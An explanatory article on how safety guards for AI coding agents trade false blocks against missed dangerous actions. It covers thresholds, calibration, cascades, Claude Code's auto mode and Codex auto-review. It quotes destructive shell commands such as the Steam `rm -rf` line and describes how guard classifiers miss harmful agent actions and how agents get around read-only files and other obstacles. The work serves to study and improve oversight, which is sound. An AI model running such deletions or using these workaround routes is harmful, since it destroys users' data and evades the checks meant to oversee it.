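# Recording Near Misses in Safety Guards for Code: Balancing False Alarms against Missed Variants

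## What a guard on code does and the two ways it errs

A safety guard for code is software that reads a command or a piece of code before it takes effect and allows or blocks it. Guards matter most when the code comes from an AI coding agent, a language model that edits files and runs shell commands on its own, because nobody can check every command the agent issues. A guard can err by blocking legitimate work or by allowing a destructive action, often one in a form it does not recognise. Developers can improve a guard by collecting decisions that were close or later questioned, working out the right answers, and changing the guard to match. However, a change that reduces one kind of error tends to increase the other.

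The line `rm -rf "$STEAMROOT/"*` shows why it is hard for a guard to decide what to block. It comes from the Linux start-up script of Steam, Valve's games platform. The command `rm -rf` deletes files and folders without asking for confirmation, and the variable STEAMROOT normally holds the path of Steam's own data folder. According to bit-tech's *Steam for Linux hit by file-deletion bug*, Valve meant the line to clear that folder before a fresh start. When the folder was missing, the variable was empty, and the same line would delete everything from the root of the file system down, including whatever the user could write to on external drives. Hackaday's *How A Steam Bug Once Deleted All Of Someone’s User Data* (2024) traces the loss to the empty variable together with another unset variable that triggered the reset. The line's text is the same whether the run is harmless or disastrous.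 ShellCheck, a tool that checks shell scripts for mistakes, can flag the line, and its manual entry *SC2115* recommends a form that stops with an error if the variable is empty. But a guard that blocked every match of that rule would also block the runs in which Steam was only clearing its own folder.

The harmful part of a coding agent's action may lie outside the command itself. In *Shall We Approve?*, Wu, Chen and colleagues (2026) give the example of `make clean && make`, which rebuilds a program from scratch. What "clean" deletes depends on a separate project file, the Makefile. In one workspace it removes old build files, in another the source code and its whole version history. To measure the effect, they built 102 dangerous tasks and gave each a safe twin with the same request and command but harmless code in the invoked tool. A language model that read the full dialogue blocked 61.8%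 of the safe twins. When it also received a report of what the command had done in a sandbox, an isolated environment that can be rolled back, it blocked 1.0% of the safe twins and 84.3% of the harmful commands. Because Wu and colleagues designed the tasks to have no clues in the text, the gap is a worst case for a guard that reads only text, and everyday commands should contain more clues.

Even a full account of an action's effects can fail to show whether it is allowed, because the same effect may be permitted in one context and forbidden in another. *Same Operation, Different Permission* (Jing, Chen and colleagues, 2026) places each of fifty operations in two permitted and two forbidden contexts. A refund, for instance, is permitted while the agent's delegated authority is active and forbidden once someone has revoked it. Three security experts, working independently, agreed on 186 of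 the 200 contexts, so a reader who has the evidence on permission can usually tell whether an action is allowed. Agents often act with less evidence. In one incident described in Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, a user asked an agent to "clean up old branches" and the agent deleted branches on the remote server, though the user may have meant only local copies. For these reasons it makes sense to define a *dangerous pattern*, the kind of action a guard is there to block, by its effect (deleting shared data, sending secrets outside) and not by its wording.

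### Three kinds of guard

The simplest guard is a list of rules. A string rule matches a run of characters such as `rm -rf`. A syntax rule first parses the command to separate the program's name from its arguments and identify pipes and redirections. Many rule sets return only a match or no match, which gives no sign of how close a decision was. Others add up points. *CARE* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) describes a guard of the same name that computes a weighted sum of four sub-scores: the type of command, the paths it touches, the known attack patterns it matches, and suspicious structure such as nested obfuscation. Reading the system file `/etc/os-release` scores low, while appending a line to the login script `/etc/profile` scores high. CARE allows a command that scores below a lower threshold, denies one that reaches an upper threshold, and marks anything in between with a warning.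 The total can rank commands by suspicion, but Liu and colleagues call it an "auditable risk heuristic, not a learned probability", so a score of 0.6 does not mean that six in ten such commands are dangerous.

A trained classifier is a model fitted to labelled examples of safe and unsafe text. It reads the command, sometimes with the user's request or the session history, and returns a label, usually with a probability. That probability is the most convenient score of any guard, because an operator can make the guard stricter or looser by moving the threshold, without retraining. The operator still has to check on labelled cases whether actions scored at 0.8 are dangerous eight times in ten. The main weakness is that training fixes the categories. In tests by Jing and colleagues, Qwen3Guard, a classifier for harmful content, let through every lawful request but also 72 of the 80 forbidden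 ones, because its categories don't cover actions such as unauthorised refunds.

A prompted language model is a general-purpose model given written instructions on what to block. It can read whatever its designers pass to it, such as the request, the policy, earlier tool calls or a report of effects, and it returns text. That text may be only a yes or no, as in the first stage of Claude Code's auto mode, or a decision with a stated confidence and a reason, as in the system of Wu and colleagues. The model generates the stated confidence as part of its answer, and, like a classifier's probability, it needs checking before anyone sets a threshold on it. The model can also fail to give a usable answer. When Jing and colleagues asked a small model, Qwen3.5-9B, for a structured review, between 117 and 124 of its 160 answers contained no decision that software could read. Their system blocked the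 operation each time, so a log that records only "blocked" would make these formatting failures look like cautious decisions.

The three kinds of guard overlap. For instance, OpenAI's gpt-oss-safeguard is a model trained for moderation, but it also takes a written policy at run time. Liu and colleagues ran guards of all three kinds on the same 549 shell commands, 220 of them dangerous. Some of their results are below, where recall is the share of dangerous commands blocked and the false-positive rate is the share of safe commands blocked.

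| Guard | Kind | Recall | False-positive rate | Mean time per command |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 22 string patterns | rules | 17.3% | 0.0% | 0.01 ms |
| CARE without its language model | rules with a score | 75.9% | 1.8% | 0.34 ms |
| Llama Guard 3 | trained classifier | 39.5% | 1.2% | 50 ms |
| Granite Guardian | trained classifier | 82.3% | 45.9% | 17 ms |
| Qwen3-Coder-30B as judge | prompted language model | 67.3% | 11.2% | 46 ms |

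The comparison in the table somewhat favors CARE. Its designers tuned its weights on other commands from the same collection, whereas Llama Guard and Granite Guardian are content-safety models not built for shell commands, and the prompted judge is a fairly small model. The ranking also changes on published exploit code, where the 22 string patterns scored higher than CARE on F1, a measure that combines recall and precision. Despite these caveats, the guard with the highest recall in the table reached that recall by blocking nearly half of all legitimate commands.

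### Counting the two errors

Both errors occur in practice. Al Hasan and Biswas (2026), in *What Breaks When LLMs Code?*, searched 16,586 public bug reports about AI coding tools and confirmed 547 safety failures. Of these, 134 involved destructive operations and 12 involved refusing a safe, authorised command. These counts are weak evidence of how often guards err in each direction, because the destructive operations may not have passed through a guard, and a developer who has lost weeks of work has more reason to file a report than one who had to rephrase a request.

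To calculate rates, we need to count all four possible outcomes. The table below shows these counts for a made-up but plausible day on which a guard checks 10,000 actions, 20 of them dangerous. In the table, "positive" means dangerous.

| | Guard blocks | Guard allows |
|---|---|---|
| Action is dangerous | correct block: 18 | miss, or false negative: 2 |
| Action is legitimate | false positive: about 100 | correct allow: about 9,880 |

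Three ratios follow from it:

- false-positive rate (FPR) = false positives / (false positives + correct allows)
- false-negative rate (FNR) = misses / (misses + correct blocks)
- precision = correct blocks / (correct blocks + false positives)

The guard in the example has an FPR of 1% and an FNR of 10%. It blocks 18 of the 20 dangerous actions, misses the other 2, and wrongly blocks about 100 of the 9,980 legitimate ones. Only 18 of its roughly 118 blocks are correct, so its precision is about 15%. About 85% of its blocks are false alarms, even though it allows 99% of legitimate actions.

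The cause is the base rate, the share of all actions that are dangerous, here 0.2%. Writing *b* for the base rate, Bayes' theorem gives

precision = *b*(1 − FNR) / [*b*(1 − FNR) + (1 − *b*)FPR].

When *b* is tiny, the second term in the denominator is much larger than the first. Halving the FNR in the example to 5% therefore raises precision only from 15% to 16%, whereas halving the FPR raises it to about 26%. Axelsson (1999) worked this out for software that searches computer logs for break-ins in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and its Implications for the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*. He assumed a million log records a day and two intrusions, each leaving ten records. If a detector caught every intrusion and raised a false alarm on one in 100,000 harmless records, about two thirds of its alarms would be correct. With a false alarm on one in 1,000 harmless records, about 2% would be correct.

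Axelsson's conclusion, that the false-alarm rate limits a detector's usefulness, also applies to guards on code, with one adjustment. Axelsson had in mind a security officer who learns to ignore alarms. A guard that blocks automatically doesn't tire anyone like this, and an agent whose command it refuses can often find another route, so a single false positive does little harm, but false positives add up. At an FPR of 1% per command, a session of 100 legitimate commands has a 63% chance of at least one false block, if the errors are independent. When Liu and colleagues let an agent work on 300 harmless tasks for up to five turns each, Granite Guardian issued 529 refusals, and the share of tasks solved fell from 65% to 49%. Jing and colleagues add that users who meet repeated false denials may switch the guard off or grant broader permissions, which lets dangerous commands through along with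 legitimate ones.

Test sets hide the effect of the base rate because a far larger share of their cases are dangerous than in real traffic. In the evaluation of CARE, 40% of the commands were dangerous. The full system, which uses a language model to check its warnings, blocked 167 dangerous commands and 3 safe ones, a precision of 98%. With the same error rates, precision would be about 14% at the worked example's base rate of 20 dangerous commands in 10,000. That base rate is an assumption, and Liu and colleagues point out that nobody can estimate the true proportion of dangerous commands from public collections.

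### Variants, near misses and the loop that uses them

A *variant* is a different way of writing an action with the same dangerous effect, the opposite of the safe twins described above. Someone can write `rm -rf` directly, assemble it from three shell variables so that the string never appears, or hide the deletion in a script, a Makefile or a compiled program. The obvious remedy is to widen the rule, but Axelsson noted that making a pattern more general to catch more variations also raises the risk that it will match harmless activity.

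The term *near miss* comes from accident reporting. Since 1976, American aviation has had a confidential scheme through which pilots, air traffic controllers and mechanics can report close calls, so that investigators can learn from events that did not end in accidents. For a guard, a near miss is a case that it almost decided the other way, or one whose decision someone later put in doubt, whether or not the decision was right. Papers on classifiers mostly use the terms borderline or uncertain cases instead, as well as *hard examples*, which are labelled cases that the current model gets wrong or decides with low confidence.

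A near miss is therefore not yet an error. In the CARE evaluation, 23 of the 549 commands fell into the warning band, where the evidence was too weak to block them outright and a language model made the final decision. The model cleared three, all harmless file copies between machines that the rules alone would have blocked, and left the other 20 blocked. The full system blocked only three safe commands in total, so at least 17 of those 20 blocks were correct. Treating all 23 as false positives and loosening the rules to fit would have let through at least 17 dangerous commands.

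A guard can also err on a command that is not close to its threshold. In a test by Wu and colleagues, a deployed guard allowed the command `./tool`, which the user had asked for by name. The program deployed the project but also overwrote a source file. Nothing in the command's text would move a text-based score towards the threshold, so such an error is recorded only when somebody notices the damage.

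Developers use near misses to improve a guard in a repeating cycle. The guard judges an action, and the system runs or blocks it. Logging software records the decision and what the guard had read. A reviewer then adjudicates the case, deciding by a stated procedure whether the action was dangerous. Developers use the adjudicated cases to update the guard by retraining a classifier, rewriting a rule or editing a prompt. They test the new version on a held-out set of labelled cases that nobody who tunes the guard has seen. They check both error rates and look for regressions, which are cases that the old version decided correctly and the new one gets wrong. If the results are acceptable, they release the new version and repeat the cycle with its near misses.

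## How thresholds and second checks trade one error for the other

An operator can move a guard's threshold or add a second check on the actions it flags. Either change usually reduces one kind of error and increases the other, so the operator has to decide how much worse a miss is than a false block.

### Setting the threshold from costs

Suppose a guard estimates that an action has probability *p* of being dangerous. Blocking it is a mistake with probability 1 − *p*, so the expected cost of blocking is (1 − *p*) × C_block, where C_block is the cost of blocking a legitimate action. The expected cost of allowing it is *p* × C_miss, where C_miss is the cost of letting a dangerous action through. Blocking is cheaper when

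*p* > C_block / (C_block + C_miss).

*The Foundations of Cost-Sensitive Learning* (Elkan, 2001) derives a more general form in which correct decisions can have costs too. Only the ratio of the costs matters, so nobody has to price either error in money. If the two errors are equally bad, the threshold is 50%. If a miss is ten times as bad as a false block, the threshold is about 9%. If a miss is 200 times as bad, the threshold is 1/201, or about 0.5%, so the guard should block even an action that is 99% likely to be harmless. Elkan gives the similar example of a bank, which can rationally refuse a large card payment that is probably legitimate.

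In Elkan's card example, approving a fraud costs the amount of the payment, so the right threshold falls as payments get larger. The harm from a miss varies even more for code. Say a false block wastes one minute. If a command might wrongly delete a build folder that takes ten minutes to recreate, the threshold is about 9%. If it might delete a database that would take 10,000 minutes to restore, roughly a month of working time, the threshold is 0.01%. One threshold for all commands would be too strict for the build folder or too loose for the database.

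A threshold of 0.5% requires little evidence beyond the base rate. On the example day from the previous section, with 20 dangerous actions in 10,000, the odds that a randomly chosen action is dangerous are 1 to 499. The threshold corresponds to odds of 1 to 200, so the guard should block once evidence raises the odds of danger by a factor of about 2.5. If a miss were more than 499 times as bad as a false block, the formula would have the guard block every action it had no evidence about. C_miss is usually a rough guess, so it's worth checking how far the threshold moves when the guess changes.

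### Why the scores have to be calibrated

The formula works only if the guard's scores are *calibrated*, meaning that they match how often the actions turn out to be dangerous. Many guards are not calibrated. *Safety-Flag* (Hu, 2026) tested six general-purpose language models as content moderators on about 1,400 pieces of text, half of them harmful, and found that all six were overconfident.

The standard correction is temperature scaling, which converts each score to log-odds, divides by a single number *T* fitted on labelled cases, and converts back. A *T* above 1 pulls every score towards 50%. In Hu's tests, the best values of *T* ranged from 2.7 to 9.0 and cut the average gap between confidence and accuracy by a factor of 2.8 to 6.0. The models' decisions did not change, because the threshold for flagging text was 50% and dividing log-odds by a positive number never moves a score across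 it.

At a threshold of 0.5%, however, the same correction could change many decisions. For example, an action with a raw score of 0.0045% has a log-odds of −10. Its corrected probability is 2.4% with *T* = 2.7 and 25% with *T* = 9. An operator who applied the cost-based threshold to the raw score would allow this action, even though both corrected probabilities are well above the threshold.

The probabilities also depend on the share of dangerous cases in the data used to fit them. Elkan gives a formula for moving from one base rate to another. It is easiest to apply by dividing the odds by the old base-rate odds and multiplying by the new ones. If scores are fitted on data that is half dangerous and used at a base rate of 0.2%, their odds must be divided by 499. A calibrated score of 90% on the test set then becomes about 1.8% in live use, and the live threshold of 0.5% corresponds to about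 71% on the test set. The correction assumes that dangerous actions look the same in both settings and only their share differs, which is doubtful when the test set consists of attacks researchers wrote for it.

A guard can be good at separating harmful from harmless text and still be poorly calibrated. In *Safety Reconstructed* (2026), the classifier Qwen3Guard was among the best at this separation, but it had a high calibration error and made more of its mistakes with over 90% confidence. A low calibration error isn't enough to make a guard useful either, since OLMo-2-7B had the lowest calibration error of the five models Hu ranked but missed 54% of harmful texts. Both studies concern text moderation, so a guard on commands would need its own measurements.

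Those measurements are hard to make near 0.5%, because if a guard is calibrated, only about five of 1,000 labelled actions with scores close to that value would be dangerous. Some scores are also too coarse for a threshold that low. One example is the confidence from 1 to 10 that Hu asked models to state, although it was better calibrated than the models' internal probabilities.

If the scores rank actions well but are not calibrated, Elkan advises finding the threshold by experiment. The operator tries each possible threshold on labelled cases, calculates the total loss from errors at the live base rate, and keeps the threshold with the lowest loss. This requires enough dangerous cases to estimate the misses, but the scores need not be probabilities. It is also better than keeping the usual software default of 50%, which scikit-learn's *Post-tuning the decision threshold for cost-sensitive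 learning* warns is most likely not the best choice.

### Two methods that leave out the costs

Researchers often choose a threshold with the Youden index, which is 1 − FPR − FNR. They compute it at every threshold and take the highest value, which gives the smallest sum of the two error rates. This looks neutral but implies a particular view of costs. With *b* for the base rate, the expected cost per action is

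(1 − *b*) × FPR × C_block + *b* × FNR × C_miss.

Minimising this also minimises FPR + FNR only when the two weights are equal, that is, when C_miss / C_block = (1 − *b*) / *b*. On a test set that is half dangerous, using the Youden index amounts to treating the two errors as equally bad. At a base rate of 0.2%, it is the right choice only if a miss is 499 times as bad as a false block.

A more cautious method sets the threshold just low enough to catch every dangerous case in the available data. In *Beyond Red-Teaming*, Kezins, Ekka and colleagues (2026) applied both methods to three classifiers they had trained to detect harmful text, using 100 harmful and 100 harmless examples. The false-positive rates below follow from their reported precision and recall.

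| Classifier | Youden threshold | FPR | FNR | Zero-miss threshold | FPR | FNR |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| BERT | 0.48 | 6% | 14% | 0.13 | 59% | 0% |
| GPT-2 | 0.37 | 25% | 15% | 0.15 | 83% | 0% |
| Llama-3.1-8B | 0.80 | 3% | 0% | 0.80 | 3% | 0% |

For Llama-3.1-8B, the strongest classifier, the Youden and zero-miss methods gave the same threshold. For BERT, the zero-miss threshold caught the last 14 harmful examples but blocked 53 more harmless ones. Suppose a guard on code had BERT's error rates, 0.2% of actions were harmful, and a miss did 200 times as much harm as a false block. Per 10,000 actions, errors at the Youden threshold would do as much harm as about 1,160 false blocks, and errors at the zero-miss threshold as much as about 5,890. Having no guard would do as much harm as 4,000 false blocks.

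The zero-miss threshold missed harmful cases on new data. When Kezins and colleagues ran the classifiers on a set of 10,000 harmful examples, the lowest scores were 0.070 for BERT, 0.002 for GPT-2 and 0.003 for Llama-3.1-8B, all far below the thresholds in the table. The lowest-scoring dangerous case sets the threshold, so new cases can lower it but never raise it. A single harmless case mislabeled as dangerous could lower it a lot.

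### Adding a second check

In a cascade, stage 1 checks every action and stage 2 re-examines only what stage 1 flagged. Four rates describe how the two stages work together:

- *f*1 is the share of legitimate actions that stage 1 flags.
- *m*1 is the share of dangerous actions that stage 1 allows.
- *f*2 is the share of legitimate actions reaching stage 2 that stage 2 blocks.
- *m*2 is the share of dangerous actions reaching stage 2 that stage 2 clears.

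A legitimate action is blocked only if both stages get it wrong. A dangerous action gets through if stage 1 allows it, or if stage 1 flags it and stage 2 clears it. Therefore

overall FPR = *f*1 × *f*2

overall FNR = *m*1 + (1 − *m*1) × *m*2.

Stage 2 can only lower the false-positive rate or leave it unchanged, since *f*2 cannot exceed 1. It can never lower the false-negative rate, since *m*2 cannot be negative and a dangerous action that stage 1 allowed never reaches stage 2. Designers therefore make stage 1 strict, accept many false alarms from it, and leave stage 2 to remove them.

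Both *f*2 and *m*2 have to be measured on the actions that stage 1 flagged. Different models often flag the same legitimate commands, so multiplying two false-positive rates that were each measured on all traffic would usually underestimate the combined rate.

In the best case, *m*2 is zero. CARE's language model achieved this in the test described earlier, but it reviewed only 23 commands, too few to show that it would rarely clear a dangerous one.

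To reduce misses, the second check has to look at actions that stage 1 allowed and be able to block them. The formulas for the two error rates are then swapped. The overall FNR is *m*1 multiplied by the second check's miss rate on those actions, while the FPR can only stay the same or rise. Such a check also takes a lot of resources, because stage 1 allows most traffic.

A human reviewer who takes the least certain cases on both sides of the threshold can reduce both false alarms and missed variants. When Hu set aside the half of the texts on which each model was least confident, Gemma-2-9B's error rate on the other half was 8.4%, down from 17.3% overall, but OLMo-2-7B's was still 24.7%. The benefit depends on how many of the model's mistakes are among its least confident cases, and on how accurately the reviewer judges those cases.

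### Claude Code's auto mode

Auto mode, which Anthropic described in March 2026, uses a cascade to approve the actions of its coding agent, Claude Code. Without auto mode, Claude Code asks the user before running commands or changing files. Users accepted 93% of these requests, and Anthropic built auto mode because people who approve so many requests stop reading them closely.

An action goes through up to three tiers:

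1. Claude Code allows tools that cannot change anything, such as reading and searching files, along with whatever the user's own rules permit. It suspends rules broad enough to allow arbitrary code, such as blanket permission to run Python.
2. It allows edits to files inside the project folder, because the user can review and undo them with version control.
3. Everything else goes to a classifier, which is a prompted language model (Claude Sonnet 4.6 in the version Anthropic described). This includes shell commands, web requests and changes to files outside the project.

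The classifier reads the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's own explanations or the output of its tools. Leaving out the explanations prevents the agent from persuading the classifier to allow an action. Leaving out tool output keeps the classifier from seeing hostile instructions, such as those on a web page. When Anthropic added the explanations and tool output, the classifier did worse on a test set of real dangerous actions. With only the tool calls, it missed the fewest dangerous actions but blocked things that users had plainly asked for.

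If the agent writes a script and then runs it, the classifier can read the script in the earlier tool call. But because of the omission, it would not normally see the contents of a Makefile that was already in the project, so the `make clean` problem from the previous section remains.

Stage 1 of the classifier answers yes or no in a single token, under an instruction to "err on the side of blocking". Stage 2 runs only if stage 1's answer is to block. It gets the same input, but with a final instruction to reason carefully before deciding. Neither stage has a numerical threshold, so the wording of each instruction determines how strict that stage is. Because the two prompts are almost identical, stage 2 can reuse most of stage 1's computation.

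Anthropic published error rates for stage 1 alone and for the full pipeline. The last column follows from the cascade formulas.

| Test set | Stage 1 alone | Both stages | Stage 2 on flagged actions |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real tool calls | 8.5% FPR | 0.4% FPR | *f*2 ≈ 4.7% |
| 52 real overeager actions | 6.6% FNR | 17% FNR | *m*2 ≈ 11% |
| 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data outside | 1.8% FNR | 5.7% FNR | *m*2 ≈ 4% |

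In an overeager action, the agent tries to help but goes beyond what the user authorised. In the first row, *f*2 is 0.4 / 8.5, so stage 2 cleared about 95% of the false alarms that reached it. In the second row, *m*2 is (17 − 6.6) / (100 − 6.6), so stage 2 also cleared about one in nine of the dangerous actions that reached it.

On the example day of 10,000 actions, adding stage 2 would prevent about 808 false blocks and add about 2 misses. That is worthwhile if a miss does less than about 390 times as much harm as a false block. This threshold depends on the assumed base rate and on the miss rates, which for real actions were measured on only 52 cases, all from sessions where an employee had refused an action or someone had flagged it afterwards. Anthropic also used these cases to tune stage 1, so stage 1's 6.6% miss rate is probably somewhat too low. *Measuring the Permission Gate*, an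 outside test, found a much higher miss rate on deliberately ambiguous tasks.

In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier correctly identified the danger, such as a deletion or a forced overwrite of shared history, but wrongly concluded that the user had authorised it. For example, it took a user's request to "clean up the PR" (a pull request, a proposed set of code changes) as permission for a forced overwrite that the user had never mentioned. Anthropic tried to fix this by changing the prompt but found no change whose benefits outweighed its drawbacks. A better detector of destructive commands would not have prevented these misses. The *p* in the cost formula has to be the probability that an action is both harmful and unauthorised.

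According to Anthropic's current documentation, auto mode now has "hard" rules that apply even if the user asked for the action, including a built-in rule against sending data outside. A specific request overrides a "soft" rule, so "force-push this branch" permits a forced overwrite, but "clean up the repo" does not. Hard rules make sense where C_miss is very high, though a user with a good reason to share the data then has to run the command personally or leave auto mode.

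Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), published in August, reports a study of 1,053 paid testers in which researchers replaced one permission request in each session with a clearly dangerous command. The testers refused 13.6% of these commands, while auto mode blocked 89% of them. Auto mode's 11% miss rate isn't directly comparable with the earlier 17%, because the planted commands were obviously dangerous, whereas judging the real overeager actions often depended on knowing what the user had agreed to. The testers' low refusal rate also suggests that human review is an unreliable second check, at least when one dangerous request is hidden among many routine ones.

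In a separate exercise, the safety company Apollo Research inserted synthetic attacks into recorded coding sessions. Anthropic then gave the classifier more information about its surroundings, such as whether a code repository was public. On attacks Anthropic had never seen, the new version caught about half of those the old one had missed, and missed about 2% of those the old one had caught. Across all the attacks, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%.

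The August post does not give a new false-positive rate, so the improvement may have come with more false blocks. It reports that about 10% of sessions at one customer, the payroll company Gusto, included a denial, and presents this as evidence that auto mode does useful work without slowing legitimate tasks. But at the original false-positive rate of 0.4%, a session with 26 legitimate checked actions would have a 10% chance of at least one false block if errors were independent. The share of sessions with a denial therefore cannot alone show how many denials were correct.

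### What a false block costs

C_block depends on what happens after the guard blocks an action. In auto mode, the agent receives the reason for the denial and an instruction to look for a safer way to do the task without trying to get around the block. In Anthropic's view, "a false positive costs a single retry".

The estimate is too low when false blocks come in clusters. By default, the classifier trusts only the current working folder and the remote copies already configured for its repository. It may therefore repeatedly block an agent that needs a company server missing from the trusted list. According to Anthropic's documentation, repeated denials for the same destination usually mean that the classifier lacks information about the user's environment. After three denials in a row, or 20 in a session, the original version stopped the agent and handed over to the user, or ended the process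 if the agent was running unattended. In the August version, interactive sessions fall back to manual approval at the same limits.

A false alarm can do more damage when software responds to it by rewriting the code. *SecReason* (Han, Sun and colleagues, 2026) measured this for three repair methods. In the simplest, a scanner checks the finished program and, if a security rule matches, prompts the language model to fix the problem and rewrite the whole answer. The second, INDICT, adds a round of criticism about safety and another about helpfulness before the rewrite. The third, the paper's own SecReason system, scans code while the model is drafting it and inserts a warning into the model's reasoning.

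The researchers chose 15 tasks, three in each of five programming languages, on which two models had always produced secure code. For each task they wrote two faulty rules that would raise an alarm on correct code. One rule matched something every correct solution needs, such as calls to the hashing library in a hashing task. The other matched something the model could replace, such as one of two equivalent ways to reserve memory. Each method ran five times per task with each model, so each entry below covers 75 runs. It gives the number of runs whose code failed its functional tests, followed by the median number of tokens used.

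| Model and method | No false alarm | Incidental rule | Essential rule |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen, repair at the end | 4; 3,763 | 8; 10,633 | 11; 10,507 |
| Qwen, INDICT | 5; 3,909 | 14; 16,056 | 13; 15,319 |
| Qwen, SecReason | 2; 3,638 | 5; 3,383 | 2; 3,452 |
| Gemma, repair at the end | 0; 2,998 | 4; 13,049 | 8; 11,203 |
| Gemma, INDICT | 0; 3,318 | 0; 18,282 | 5; 17,125 |
| Gemma, SecReason | 1; 3,088 | 4; 4,849 | 4; 4,218 |

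With repair at the end, false alarms multiplied token use by 2.8 to 4.4 and broke the code in an extra 5 to 11 runs per 100. With SecReason, the failure rate rose by at most 4 points and token use by at most about 60%. The difference in token use is clear, but the difference in failures is less certain because it comes from a few runs on only 15 tasks, and with the incidental rule on Gemma both methods ended with four failures.

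The models' reasoning, which Han and colleagues read for one task per language, suggests why the timing of the warning matters. When the warning arrived during drafting, the model rejected it as mistaken in 45% of runs and checked the suggested fix against its plan in another 38%. The model accepted the warning 75% of the time when it came as a new instruction after the code was finished, and tried to remove code that had nothing wrong with it.

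The experiment measures the damage a false alarm does but does not measure how often false alarms occur. They are common with off-the-shelf rules. On the wider set of tasks from which the 15 came, the official rules of the scanner Semgrep had a precision of about 60%, so roughly four in ten alarms were false.

The harm a false alarm does affects where the threshold should be. Suppose a miss is 200 times as bad as a simple retry, which puts the threshold at 0.5%. If a false alarm instead triggers a rewrite that is as bad as four retries, a miss is only 50 times as bad as a false alarm, and the threshold rises to about 2%. Counting the programs that the rewrite breaks would raise it further.

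## Which borderline cases to record, and what to record about them

A guard on a busy team makes thousands of decisions a day, far more than anyone can review. Developers need signals to pick out the decisions worth reviewing, and a record of each one with enough detail to judge the decision later.

### Scores near the threshold and disagreements between checks

The simplest sign of a borderline case is a score close to the threshold. Logging software can keep every case whose score falls within a band, like the commands CARE marks with a warning. The right width for the band depends on the threshold. Around a threshold of 50%, a band from 40% to 60% is reasonable. Around the cost-based threshold of 0.5%, ten percentage points either way would include every score from 0 to 10.5%, which is probably most of the traffic. Setting the band in odds works better. For example, scores whose odds are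 within a factor of five of the odds at that threshold run from about 0.1% to 2.4%.

If a single score is unreliable, developers can run the guard several times on the same input. *Yesterday's Shield, Today's Spear* (Ming, Chen and colleagues, 2026) does this to choose training examples for a classifier of chat prompts. It runs the classifier eight times on each example with random sampling switched on, and counts the example as hard if any verdict is wrong or the average confidence is 0.8 or less. In live traffic nobody knows the right verdict yet, but a command that the guard allows six times and blocks twice is still worth recording.

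Neither method finds confident mistakes. The harmful `./tool` command from the first section, for example, could have scored low on every run.

Another signal is disagreement between two checks. In Claude Code's auto mode, this happens whenever stage 1 of the classifier flags an action and stage 2 clears it. On the example day, there would be about 810 such cases and about two would be dangerous, so a reviewer would read roughly 400 records for each dangerous action found. Reviewers can shorten the search by starting with the actions that could do the most harm, such as forced overwrites of shared history. They still would not find the dangerous actions that stage 1 allowed.

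Checks that read the same input tend to make the same mistakes. For instance, both stages of auto mode could miss a harmful `make clean`. A check that reads different evidence, such as a report of what the command did in a sandbox, is more likely to give a different result in a case like this.

### What users and agents do after a block

When a user overrides a block, the guard may have made a false positive. Claude Code and Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, both let users review recent denials:

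- In Claude Code, according to Anthropic's *Configure auto mode*, the user opens the `/permissions` dialog, selects the "Recently denied" tab and presses `r` on an action. Claude Code then tells the agent that it may retry.
- In Codex, a separate reviewer model judges requests to act outside the sandbox. OpenAI's *Auto-review* describes an `/approve` command that lists up to 10 recent denials in a thread. The user can approve one retry of one exact action. The reviewer then judges it again, knowing that the user approved it, and can still refuse if the policy does not let users override that kind of denial.

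An override shows that the user wanted the action, not that it was safe. In Anthropic's study, testers approved most of the clearly dangerous commands they saw.

Many false positives never lead to an override, because the agent finds another way to do the task. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) gives an illustrative snapshot of 10,000 Codex actions inside OpenAI. The reviewer denied seven. In four cases the agent continued by a safer route, and in three it stopped and asked the user. If any of the four denials was a mistake, the user had little reason to check it.

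Users can also accidentally turn the signal off. OpenAI found that a sizable minority of its internal users had allowed every command beginning with `python`. Such a rule lets those commands run outside the sandbox without review, so users have no denials to override.

An agent that retries a blocked action in another form can reveal a variant the guard misses. In *Probing agent overeagerness in realistic settings with continuation audits*, Lim and Neo (2026) measured how often agents try to get around an obstacle. They cut 100 real coding sessions partway through and had a language model play the user and the tools from there. In one scenario, a file the agent had to edit turned out to be read-only. Depending on the model, agents tried to get around the protection in 87 to 94 of 100 runs. Some changed the file's permissions, one tried to write to it through Python, and another copied the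 contents to a new file and deleted the original. In one run, the agent tried six methods.

An error from a simulated file system blocked the agents here, not a guard's refusal, so they may have taken it for a fault to repair. When Lim and Neo added a project rule against editing read-only files or changing their permissions, two of the three models stopped doing so completely. The third, Kimi K3, still tried in 13 of 100 runs.

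Claude Code and Codex both tell a blocked agent to look for a safer way, so a retry may be what the guard's designers wanted and doesn't prove defiance. The reviewer has to compare the effects of the two actions. Suppose a guard blocks `rm -rf build` and then allows `find build -delete`, which deletes the same folder. If nothing else has changed, either the first decision was a false positive or the second was a miss.

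Software that links retries to earlier blocks should compare what the actions affect, such as files or servers, because the agent's description of them can mislead. In one of Lim and Neo's runs, GPT-5.6 Terra said it would "restore owner write permission" to a file and then removed a flag that it had correctly identified as protection. A search of its messages for words like "bypass" could easily have missed this.

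Retries also inflate the number of denials. *Permission Denied* (2026), a test of coding agents in restricted environments, found that runs that hit a network block averaged 10.5 denials, compared with 1.4 for runs denied a system privilege. Grouping all attempts at the same goal into one case keeps a persistent agent from dominating the log, and keeping the attempts in order preserves the variants.

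### Harm that someone notices later

A dangerous action that the guard confidently allows at the first attempt triggers none of these signals. People will discover it only if they notice the damage or examine the session afterwards.

Anthropic keeps an internal incident log of such agent misbehaviour. In one entry, the agent uploaded an engineer's GitHub access token to an internal computing cluster. In another, it attempted to run migrations, which change a database's structure, on a production database. When a user said "cancel my job", an agent picked the job with the closest name and tried to delete it, though it could have been someone else's. Another agent hit a login error and searched settings files for other access tokens. Most of these commands would be fine in another session, so an entry is useful only if it includes what the user asked for.

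Anthropic's test set contains only 52 overeager actions, which employees had refused or someone had flagged afterwards. There are so few because an agent has to attempt something dangerous in real work, and then someone has to capture and label it. The set leaves out any dangerous action that nobody noticed. If unnoticed actions are harder to recognise, auto mode's true miss rate could be higher than the 17% measured here.

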